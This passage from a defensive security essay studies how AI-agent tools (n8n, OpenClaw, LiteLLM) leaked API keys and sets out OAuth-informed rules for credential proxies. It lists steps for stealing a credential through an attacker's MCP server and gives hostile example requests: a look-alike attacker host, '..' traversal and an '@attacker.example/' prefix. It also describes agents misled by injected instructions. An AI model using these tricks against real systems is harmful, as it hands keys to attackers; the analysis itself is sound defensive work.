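The first flaw was in the HTTP Request node, the only place where the rule is documented to apply. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-25631* (2026), an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, a logged-in user could send a credential to unintended domains if the credential's domain list contained a wildcard such as `*.example.com`.

n8n's advisory, which GCVE's *GHSA-2XCX-75H9-VR9H* (2026) carries in full, doesn't specify which comparison failed. The description fits a suffix test with a missing dot, the error that lets `*.print.example` cover `blueprint.example`. This would explain why only wildcard entries were unsafe, but other errors would too, such as a star that matches more of the address than it should.

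The fix came out 11 weeks before the advisory, which was published on February 4, 2026. The release notes for version 1.121.0 (n8n, 2025), published on November 18, probably refer to it in the line "Improve domain validation". Administrators who read only those notes had little reason to think that keys were at risk or to hurry the upgrade.

For anyone who couldn't upgrade, n8n recommended replacing wildcards with explicit domains, letting only trusted people edit workflows, and checking existing workflows that used restricted credentials. Red Hat gives Keycloak users the same advice about wildcards in redirect URIs.

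### Code that never made the comparison

The next n8n flaw was in a server endpoint, `/rest/dynamic-node-parameters/options`. GitLab's *GHSA-3875-8gcx-7v46* (2026) reports that any logged-in user with access to a credential could use this endpoint to make n8n's server send that credential to a host not on the credential's allowlist. An attacker didn't need to run a workflow.

The flaw in the AI Agents module, CVE-2026-59207, is the one closest to the secret proxies. An n8n agent can use tools from outside MCP servers, and the workflow's author supplies each server's address and picks a credential for it. The attack took three steps:

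1. A user with use-only access to a restricted credential adds an MCP tool to an agent and enters the address of their own server.
2. The user selects the restricted credential for that tool.
3. The user runs the agent, and n8n sends the request to the user's server with the secret attached.

*CVE-2026-59207*, an analysis by the security company SecureLayer7, traces the flaw to how n8n had organized its code. The domain check was part of the HTTP Request node, but the agent module built and sent its own requests, so it never ran the check. The patch adds the same check to the agent module and stops the request with an error if the host is not on the list.

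According to Corgea's *n8n*, which reproduces the advisory, the flaw affected only installations that had turned the module on and shared at least one restricted credential with an ordinary member. Administrators who couldn't upgrade could turn the module off or share credentials only with people they fully trusted, but n8n warned that these steps would not remove all of the risk.

Two more disclosures followed on July 22, less than two weeks later. GitLab's *CVE-2026-65596* (2026) describes the first flaw, in the node for GraphQL, a query language for web services. The user types in the address, as in the HTTP Request node, but the GraphQL node didn't apply the rule.

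The second flaw affected several nodes that call language models and let the user change the base URL, the first part of the service's address. GitLab's *GHSA-64xh-79j6-r5v8* (2026) reports that the nodes didn't check the user-supplied base URL, so a user could enter their own server's address and collect the key. SecureLayer7's *n8n* gives the example of a node that should send an OpenAI key to `api.openai.com` but sends it to the attacker instead. The patch again copied the check into each affected node. Rapid7 lists the flaw as CVE-2026-72771.

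When the check is copied into each node, every copy has to be used correctly, and the GraphQL node soon failed again. A user normally picks the node's login type from a menu, but a formula can also set it while the workflow runs. When a formula set the type, according to NixOS's *n8n before 1.123.69 Allowed-Domains Bypass via GraphQL Node*, the node treated every attached credential as active. If a user attached two of different types, it checked the domain list of the first and sent both. A user could therefore put a credential that allowed their own server first and a restricted one second, and the node would send both to that server.

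OAuth software has failed in the same way. ApiFest and Cloudflare's library did not compare the redirect URI with the registered ones when the authorization request arrived. As with n8n, a developer who read the rule in the settings or documentation would have thought it was enforced. The second GraphQL flaw is more like the duplicate `code` parameter, where a program built to handle one value received two.

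### Tokens and keys in other tools

OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent that people can reach through chat apps, had two flaws. The first was in its optional extension for Microsoft Teams. OpenClaw downloads attachments and images sent to it through Teams, and if a server refuses the request, it may retry with an access token. The extension was supposed to send that token only to hosts on a list. GitLab's *CVE-2026-28481* (2026) reports that the extension matched hosts to the list by the end of their names, and that the list included domains on which many unrelated customers have their own subdomains.

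An attacker could therefore put a file on one of these subdomains, refuse the first download request, and receive the token with the second. The attack only required that OpenClaw receive a message containing the link. The comparison worked as written, but the entries covered hosts that belonged to strangers. Auth0, a commercial login provider, advises against wildcard subdomains in OAuth callback addresses because an attacker may take one over. OpenClaw's attacker didn't need to take over a subdomain, because anyone could get one by becoming a customer. OpenClaw fixed the flaw in version 2026.2.1.

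The other flaw was in how OpenClaw handled redirects. An operator can configure OpenClaw to send extra headers, such as an API key, to a particular MCP server. Corgea's *MCP Streamable HTTP redirects could forward configured custom headers to another origin* explains that if the server redirected a request to another origin, OpenClaw followed the redirect and sent the headers there too. A key could leak this way if the MCP server was malicious or hacked, or if an attacker could make an honest server redirect.

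In 2013, browsers carried OAuth tokens to other sites in much the same way. The redirect matters most when a legitimate MCP server has an open redirector. A malicious server gains little from the redirect because it already has the key. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-53840* (2026) gives 2026.5.12 as the first safe version.

LiteLLM is a gateway that companies place between their software and AI providers. It holds the company's provider keys and adds them to outgoing calls, so it is a kind of secret proxy. OSV's *CVE-2026-84377* (2026) reports that any logged-in user could redirect a call to their own server and receive the company's key.

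LiteLLM checked requests for settings that change the destination, but its list was incomplete. It also missed settings placed inside another field, in the path, or in form data written with brackets. When a setting got through, the gateway sent the company's key to the user's address. Wang and colleagues had found a similar gap at the cloud platform that took its return address from `state`. LiteLLM fixed the flaw in versions 1.88.6 and 1.96.2.

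The last case is a command-line tool that connects to a vendor's service over MCP. Users can set the service's address with an environment variable or the `configure` command. With the environment variable, the tool accepted only the vendor's own hosts over HTTPS. With `configure`, according to CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-81101*, it accepted any address, saved it beside the user's access token, and sent the token there on every later request. To exploit this, an attacker had to persuade the user to run the command with the attacker's address. Version 0.2.5 applies the environment variable's check to both settings.

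### What twelve disclosures can show

Eight of the twelve flaws come from a missing comparison and two from a wrong one (Claude Code's prefix test and n8n's wildcard). In the other two, involving Hugging Face and Teams, the software compared names as intended, but its allowlist covered pages or hosts that strangers controlled. Requiring exact host names would have prevented only the Claude Code, n8n and Teams flaws.

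These proportions are weak evidence about agent software in general, since n8n accounts for six of the twelve flaws and five of the eight missing comparisons. n8n's code may be unusually weak here, or people may have looked harder after the first disclosures. The count also depends on how vendors group flaws. One advisory covers several AI nodes, while two cover the GraphQL node alone.

Philippaerts and colleagues ran the same tests on every OAuth provider they studied, so they could calculate a failure rate. The twelve disclosures can't provide one because they don't show how many programs have destination rules, how many of those anyone has examined, or how many passed. Vendors that run their software only in their own cloud can also fix a flaw without publishing anything.

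n8n's missing checks all had much the same result, with a key ending up on a server that the attacker controls, but their severity scores differ. On version 3 of the standard scale, which runs to 10, INCIBE's *CVE-2026-59207* (2026) gives the MCP connector 6.5, while GitLab's entries give the AI nodes 7.7, the GraphQL node 8.5 and the options endpoint 9.1.

None of the twelve concerns the six secret proxies compared earlier. That is weak evidence that the proxies are safe, because several are new and few outsiders have published tests. Ghosh has already found several faults in one of them by fuzzing.

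## Which OAuth rules a secret proxy should adopt

A secret proxy relies on a list of destinations where it may send a key. The IETF considered a similar list for OAuth access tokens and rejected it, for reasons that could also apply to proxies.

### The list the IETF rejected

In section 4.10.3 of RFC 9700, Lodderstedt and colleagues consider having the authorization server tell clients where its tokens are safe to use. The server could publish the names of its resource servers:

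```
"resource_servers": [
  "email.somesite.example",
  "storage.somesite.example",
  "video.somesite.example"
]
```

An authorization server could give clients a list of the right server addresses, or return the right address with each token. Neither field is part of a standard. If someone tricked a client into contacting a counterfeit server, the client would see that the address did not match and would not send the token.

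The weakness is that the client has to enforce the list. Lodderstedt and colleagues cite research in which many clients skipped security checks such as comparing `state` or implemented them incorrectly, and they expect clients to fail at this check too. They also prefer to put the security logic in servers because there are far fewer servers than clients. They propose audience-restricted and sender-constrained tokens as alternatives, which the resource server checks.

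Part of this objection doesn't apply to a proxy. It runs outside the agent, so injected text can't make it skip the check. One proxy can also serve many programs whose developers would otherwise each have to write the check. Its developers have more reason to get the check right because it is what their customers want. The developer of an OAuth client, by contrast, can leave out the `state` comparison and notice no difference in normal use.

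But n8n also held its credentials on a central server, and some of its nodes sent them without checking the destination. A proxy with several code paths to the network has a smaller version of the problem the IETF saw in clients.

The IETF could also reject the list because it had better options, which proxies often lack. Posta (2026), in *Credential Injection Patterns for AI Agents*, an article about a commercial gateway, points out that API keys, GitHub's personal tokens and most tokens for online services are not sender-constrained. The proxy's list may be the only control on where those credentials go. Section 4.10.3 is therefore a good reason to use restricted tokens wherever a service supports them, but it doesn't justify dropping the list elsewhere.

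One part of the rejected design would be useful to proxies, a list written by the authorization server, which knows its own resource servers. A proxy's user has to work out the hosts from an API's documentation or trust a vendor's list, such as Docker's six hosts for GitHub. If each service published the hosts that accept its keys, users wouldn't have to do either.

### How an API call differs from a callback

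API paths vary too much for a proxy to compare whole addresses, as OAuth does with callbacks. The proxy has to find the host within the address and compare that, so its rule will cover many pages. Unlike an authorization server, which hands the browser a string to parse again, a proxy opens the connection itself and can connect to the same host it compared. This removes one chance for two programs to read an address differently, but the server at the other end may still follow a different host named in the request, as Ghosh found.

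A proxy can also apply a rule that an authorization server can't, because it receives redirects before anyone follows them. In 2013, Facebook could not stop Skype's redirector from forwarding tokens, because the browser had already left Facebook.

A wrong decision by a secret proxy does more harm than one by an OAuth authorization server, because the proxy releases a reusable key and has no second check like the one at OAuth's code exchange. The proxy should therefore refuse unclear requests.

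Finally, a proxy that serves many agents needs to know which agent is making each request, or any agent could use every secret the proxy holds. The set of permitted destinations for a secret *s* then depends on the agent *a* as well, so *R*(*s*) becomes *R*(*a*, *s*).

*Governing Enterprise AI Traffic at Scale* (2026) describes a company gateway that identifies each caller by an internal credential. Developers have a token tied to their corporate identity, applications have one tied to their registration, and platforms acting for users get signed, time-limited tokens that name the user and the platform. *Caging the Agents* (2026), a design for AI agents in healthcare, instead gives each agent its own small proxy in a neighboring container, called a sidecar. The sidecar serves one agent, so it doesn't have to identify the caller.

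The proxy must get the user's identity from something the agent can't choose. WorkOS's *How to let AI agents act on behalf of users* (2026) describes a proxy that reads the user's ID from a request header, and warns that the WorkOS key that authenticates the request stays where the agent runs. A hijacked agent could presumably use that key to send a request with another user's ID.

### Compare the whole origin

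The IETF's *HTTP Semantics*, the main standard for web requests, defines an origin as the scheme, host and port, with the scheme and host in lowercase and the default port filled in. `https://Example.Com/happy.js` therefore has the origin (https, example.com, 443). A proxy can come closest to OAuth's exact matching by requiring all three parts of a request's origin to equal those in the secret's rule.

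A flaw in HTTP.jl, a web library for the Julia programming language, shows why checking only the host is not enough. According to Julia's *JLSEC-2026-613* (2026), the library kept credentials on a redirect as long as the host name stayed the same. A redirect from HTTPS to HTTP therefore sent them unencrypted, and a redirect to another port could send them to a different service.

Wang and colleagues tested OAuth providers and found parsing flaws only in those that used pattern matching, which supports exact matching. Their results only partly apply to proxies, because a proxy can't avoid parsing the address.

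Naming the scheme and port adds little work, because a proxy can fix HTTPS and port 443 for every rule, as fnox does. A more serious problem is that an origin can be too broad. Every repository on Hugging Face, including an attacker's, has the same origin, so a rule for a host like this also needs to limit the path.

### Regional and customer hosts

Suppose the printing service runs its API in four regions, at names such as `eu.api.print.example`, and gives each of its 200 business customers a host such as `acme.print.example`. A developer would rather write one wildcard than list 204 host names.

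A tool could write the names instead. The developer enters the pattern once, and the tool looks up the existing hosts that match it, shows them to the developer and stores their full names. The proxy then compares exact names and never interprets a star. If the tool expands the star too broadly, the developer can see the extra hosts in the list.

The proxy may not need a list of customer hosts, because an agent usually works for one customer at a time. The proxy can fill in `acme` when the session starts, as long as it takes the customer's name from the operator's records and not from the agent's request.

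Expansion works badly if new hosts appear faster than anyone updates the list. For example, an agent that tests preview deployments could not use its key on a new deployment until someone added the host. Expansion also fails if the service chooses a host while answering a request, as some download services do. A list can also keep a host for too long. If the printing service abandons `acme.print.example` and an attacker takes it over, the old entry will still allow the proxy to send the key there. The list is still safer than a wildcard, which has the same weakness for every name under the domain, but list entries should expire.

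For preview hosts, a reasonable compromise is a wildcard that covers one label under a domain the company uses for nothing else, paired with a key that can access only test data. Nobody has measured how often expanded lists go stale or how often proxy wildcards leak keys, so these recommendations rest on argument and the OAuth record. fnox and Tracekit Box don't allow wildcards in their secret rules, which shows only that some users can manage without them.

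### Match paths segment by segment

An origin rule controls who receives the key, while a path rule limits what the agent can do with it. A plain prefix such as `/repos/print-example/shop` also matches `/repos/print-example/shop-private`. Anthropic's Filesystem MCP Server had the same flaw in its folder checks. The proxy should instead split the pattern and the path at each slash and compare them piece by piece. A `*` should match exactly one piece, and the proxy should allow `**` only at the end of the pattern, where it matches everything that remains.

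Matching paths by pattern brings back a technique the IETF gave up because developers kept getting it wrong. A mistake does less harm here. If the origin is right and the path matcher is wrong, the agent can do something the operator meant to forbid, but the key still goes to the service that accepts it. The exception is a host that routes different paths to different customers' programs, where a wrong path could give the key to another customer. An operator should not send a key to such a host.

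Path rules should list permitted paths, not forbidden ones. GitHub ignores case in owner and repository names, so `/repos/Print-Example/SHOP` reaches the same repository as the lowercase version. If a case-sensitive list contains only the lowercase path, a list of permitted paths refuses the other spelling, which is a minor nuisance, but a list of forbidden paths lets it through.

Path rules can't restrict much on some APIs. A GraphQL service typically receives every operation at one path, so the rule can't distinguish reads from deletes, and the operator has to limit the key's permissions instead.

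### Refuse ambiguous addresses

The advice to validate an address without sanitizing it applies nearly unchanged to proxies. HTTP Semantics says programs should treat a user name in an untrusted address as an error, because it is probably there to disguise the real host. The same standard lets the recipient of a header containing line breaks or null characters either reject the message or replace those characters with spaces. A proxy that holds keys should reject the message.

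The proxy should also refuse requests that contain backslashes, `..` path segments, or repeated `Host` or `Authorization` headers. The host it connects to must match every host named in the request. This check would have caught the worst fault Ghosh found in Tracekit Box.

The objection is that honest programs spell addresses in different ways. Under the rules of HTTP Semantics, for instance, these two addresses mean the same thing:

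```
https://api.print.example/~anna/list
https://API.print.example:443/%7Eanna/list
```

A proxy can limit its refusals to characters that could change which host or folder an address refers to, since refusing every unusual spelling would break working software. An encoded slash could change the folder, for example, while an encoded space is harmless. Some APIs may need an encoded slash, for instance to fit a folder path into one segment, and the rules for those APIs would have to permit it explicitly.

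Removing headers is a justified exception. Lodderstedt and colleagues require reverse proxies, which pass outside requests to a company's own servers, to clean up any security-relevant incoming header. Otherwise, an attacker could add a header that falsely gives the sender's network address as a permitted one. Removing a header is safer than repairing an address because no later check depends on the removed value.

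Known attacks support refusal, including those on Keycloak's wildcards. No experiment has compared proxies that refuse odd addresses with proxies that repair them.

### Decide again at every redirect

A web program that follows a redirect repeats its request at the new address. HTTP Semantics tells the program to drop an `Authorization` header that it generated itself, but only to "consider removing" one that the calling program supplied. Browsers are now stricter. Ishibashi (2023) announced in *Intent to Ship* that Chrome would drop the header whenever the origin changes, and reported that all browser makers agreed.

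Other web libraries have often got this wrong. Seven have disclosed flaws since January 2025. One was HTTP.jl, and the others were these:

- Go's web client dropped the header correctly when a redirect led from `a.com` to `b.com/1`. According to INCIBE's *CVE-2024-45336* (2025), it then restored the header if `b.com/1` redirected to `b.com/2`.
- AsyncHttpClient, a Java library, has an option to remove credentials on redirects. GitLab's *AsyncHttpClient leaks authorization credentials to untrusted domains on cross-origin redirects* (2026) reports that the library still passed on the stored password with the option switched on.
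- Four libraries sent credentials to the new address whatever its origin: HTTP::Tiny for Perl (INCIBE's *CVE-2026-7017* (2026)), urllib for Node.js (INCIBE's *CVE-2026-55553* (2026)), cpp-httplib for C++ (Red Hat (2026)), and Vert.x for Java (Eclipse Foundation's *Credential headers forwarded on cross-origin HTTP redirect in Eclipse Vert.x HttpClient*).

A proxy that adds a key and lets one of these libraries follow redirects could leak the key, even if its own rule is perfect. The safest rule is for the proxy never to follow redirects and to pass them to the agent instead. The agent's next request then carries a placeholder or no credential and needs a new decision from the proxy. WorkOS's proxy doesn't follow redirects. The seven flaws are good evidence for the rule, but Kenney and colleagues did not test redirect chains, and no other published test shows how secret proxies handle them.

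Refusing the new address outright would break common APIs. GitHub's *Best practices for using the REST API* tells developers to assume that any request may lead to a redirect, and to follow it. For example, when a program asks to download a build file, GitHub redirects it to a separate address that expires after one minute. The operator has to let the agent reach that host but should never let the token go there. If the download host changes often, a wildcard in the network list does less harm than one in the secret's rule, although it would still let a misled agent send data to more places.

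### One check for all traffic

A proxy can't check requests that go around it. *aiAuthZ* (2026), the design of a gateway that approves agents' tool calls, offers three remedies, from weakest to strongest:

1. A command-line tool scans the agent's configuration and reports an error if the agent also has built-in shell, file or web tools that overlap with the gateway's.
2. The operator puts the agent on an internal network whose only exit is the gateway.
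3. Only the gateway holds the secrets, so an agent that gets around it has no key.

The third remedy is enough to protect the key. ZenML's *Credential Proxy* describes a small demonstration in which the agent can reach a mock wiki directly, but the wiki refuses the request because only the proxy can add the required header. The operator still needs to lock down the network to protect other data that the agent can read.

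Inside the proxy, one function should make every decision about whether a secret may be sent to a destination, and the code that sends requests should have no other way to get a secret. A developer who adds a new feature then doesn't have to remember to copy the check. The main evidence for this design is n8n's repeated failures.

A central proxy gives attackers one valuable target. Posta, who favors proxies, warns that the gateway's database holds every user's tokens. Hartman (2026), in *Credential Broker for Agents (CB4A)*, a proposal submitted to the IETF, cites a March 2026 attack on LiteLLM in which attackers put a program that steals credentials into the published packages. Hartman gives an estimate of more than 300 GB of compressed credentials for the whole campaign, affecting about 500,000 corporate identities. A proxy also adds a step to every call, and agents stop working if it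 fails.

Hartman proposes separating the component that approves a request from the one that holds the credentials, so that breaking into one doesn't give an attacker both. Sidecars also spread the risk, but the one in *Caging the Agents* still holds keys for Anthropic, GitHub, Linear and Google Cloud. An operator could run many copies of the same proxy, each with only its own agent's secrets. This would keep the check in one codebase without putting all the keys in one place. Nobody has tested this arrangement against a shared gateway.

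### Who may add a destination

OAuth lets some clients name an unregistered redirect URI if they authenticate and send the request directly to the authorization server. A secret proxy should not adopt this exception. An authenticated OAuth client presumably sends what its developers intended, but an agent can prove its identity and still be following an attacker's instructions. A new destination for a secret should therefore come from a person, through a channel the agent can't use.

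Ghosh's system has such a channel for network access. If an agent asks for an unlisted host, the proxy holds the connection for up to two minutes while a person on the host machine decides, and nothing inside the agent's virtual machine can approve it. Each virtual machine can have at most 16 requests waiting and can open at most 30 a minute, which limits how often an agent can interrupt the person. Approving a host opens a connection but does not add the host to any secret's rule.

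A person who sees only a name such as `api-print.example` can't tell whether the printing service owns it, and an attacker would choose a name that looks right. The approval screen should therefore show which secret the agent wants to use and which host would receive it. The person should check the host against the service's own documentation, not anything the agent found or wrote.

There are two objections to requiring human approval. An agent that runs overnight can't wait for a person, and operators who have to approve every new service may grow careless or remove the restrictions. No experiment has measured how well people judge these requests, so the case for approval is based only on reasoning.

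Another design doesn't let the agent choose the host. With nono_proxy, an open-source library, the agent calls `http://localhost:PORT/openai/v1/chat`, and the proxy sends the request to `https://api.openai.com/v1/chat` with the real key. The proxy therefore has no agent-supplied host to check. This resembles the 2013 advice that an authorization server could ignore the requested address and use the registered one.

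The agent still supplies the path, so the proxy must join it to the API's address carefully. If the proxy just appended the agent's text to `https://api.openai.com`, text beginning with `@attacker.example/` would make the attacker's server the host. The design also requires software that lets the user change the API's address.

### Tokens that expire and requests that carry a signature

Destination rules will sometimes fail, so it helps if a leaked credential expires quickly. Hartman recommends that a broker use its long-lived key to get a token that lasts seconds or minutes and give that token to the agent. The draft lists ways to do this at AWS, Google Cloud, Azure and GitHub. Hartman treats a proxy that adds the key to requests as a fallback for services that can't issue short-lived tokens.

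Posta argues that most companies should do the opposite. The agent would still hold a usable token, and a company can't exchange an employee's corporate login for a token at GitHub, Slack or Salesforce. Each user has to approve access in a browser, and the gateway then has to store the token.

A proxy can combine the two approaches by getting a short-lived token and adding it to the request, so the agent never holds the token. Permit.io's proxy does this for AWS. According to *Credentials & Connections*, its temporary credentials last between 15 minutes and 12 hours.

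If the service offers audience-restricted tokens, the proxy should request each token for the address it is about to contact. Otherwise, an error in matching the destination can still leak a usable token.

Request signing goes further, because the secret never leaves the proxy. AWS uses a method called Signature Version 4. The sender first arranges the request in a fixed format (the example is a request to list users, without a body):

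```
GET
/
Action=ListUsers&Version=2010-05-08
host:iam.amazonaws.com
x-amz-date:20261205T101500Z

host;x-amz-date
<hash of the empty body>
```

It then hashes this text and builds a second one from the result:

```
AWS4-HMAC-SHA256
20261205T101500Z
20261205/us-east-1/iam/aws4_request
<hash of the text above>
```

The sender signs the second text with a key derived from the secret and adds the signature to the request. AWS repeats the calculation and refuses the request if the signatures differ.

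Suppose a matching error makes the proxy sign a request for `attacker.example` and send it there. The signature covers that host name, so AWS will refuse the request if the attacker forwards it. An attacker who obtains a request signed for AWS can usually replay it only within five minutes, and can't change the parts the signature covers. The signature is also limited to one date, region and service.

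The proxy must sign each request for the host it connects to. If it signs a request for AWS but connects to the attacker, the attacker gets that one valid request.

Signing takes more work than replacing a placeholder because the proxy has to build the signature after the agent finishes the request. It also works only with services that support it. If a misled agent makes a harmful request that the rules allow, the proxy will still sign it.

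### A policy for one token

The printing service has an agent called `release-helper`, which reads the issues and build files of one GitHub repository and writes comments. This policy for its token adds the agent's identity, an expiry date and a separate network list to fnox's rule format. Nobody has tested the policy, which is based on the incidents and arguments above.

```
secret   GITHUB_TOKEN
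agent    release-helper
origin   https, api.github.com, 443
header   authorization
allow    GET   /repos/print-example/shop/**
         POST  /repos/print-example/shop/issues/*/comments
expires  2026-12-31

network  release-helper
         https, api.github.com, 443
         https, files.storage.example, 443
```

The second network entry stands for the host that serves GitHub's downloads (the name is invented). The proxy handles every request with the same function:

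```
decide(connection, request):
  agent = identity of the connection
  if the request is ambiguous:                 refuse
  target = origin of the request
  if target is not in network[agent]:          refuse
  if the request contains no placeholder:      forward as is

  rule = rules[agent, placeholder]
  if there is no rule, or it has expired:      refuse
  if a placeholder is outside rule.header:     refuse
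  if target is not equal to rule.origin:       refuse
  if method and path fit no line of the rule:  refuse

  connect to target and verify its certificate
  put the secret in rule.header and send
  remove the secret from the reply
  return the reply without following redirects
```

A request is ambiguous if it has any of the faults described earlier, such as a user name in the address, a `..` step, an encoded slash, or two hosts that don't match.

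The table shows eight requests. The agent puts the placeholder only in the `Authorization` header unless otherwise noted. Addresses that start with `/` are on `https://api.github.com`.

| | Request | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `GET /repos/print-example/shop/issues/9` | Send with token | Fits the rule |
| 2 | `GET https://api.github.com.attacker.example/repos/print-example/shop` | Refuse | Host is not on the network list |
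| 3 | `GET /repos/print-example/shop/../../mallory/notes` | Refuse | Path contains `..` |
| 4 | `GET /repos/print-example/shop-private/contents/keys` | Refuse | `shop-private` is not `shop` |
| 5 | `POST /repos/print-example/shop/issues/9/comments`, with the placeholder also in the comment | Refuse | Placeholder is outside the permitted header |
| 6 | `GET /repos/print-example/shop/actions/artifacts/41/zip` | Send with token, return the redirect | Fits the rule |
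| 7 | `GET https://files.storage.example/41.zip`, with no placeholder | Forward without token | Host is on the network list only |
| 8 | `POST /repos/print-example/shop/issues/9/comments`, with customer records in the comment | Send with token | Fits the rule |

Requests 6 and 7 make up one download. GitHub answers request 6 with a redirect to the storage host, which the proxy passes to the agent. The agent's software then sends request 7, which the proxy treats as a new request. If the software wrongly kept the placeholder in the header, the proxy would refuse request 7 because the storage host is not the rule's origin. The download would fail, but the token would be safe. The agent sees the temporary download address, so if misled, it could pass the address to someone else, who would have a minute to use it.

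The path rule also needs some upkeep. If the company renames the repository, GitHub redirects requests to the new name, and the proxy refuses the redirected requests until someone edits the rule. Even without a proxy, a rename can break software that downloads files. In one GitHub bug report, a program built for exactly one redirect got a file's description instead of the file after a rename added a second redirect.

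Request 8 is the only one the policy handles incorrectly. If the repository is public, the agent has published the customer records even though the proxy followed its rules. Ghosh concedes the same limit for Tracekit Box, which controls which hosts an agent may contact but doesn't check what the agent sends them. The operator could remove the `POST` line and have a person write the comments, or keep customer records out of the agent's reach.
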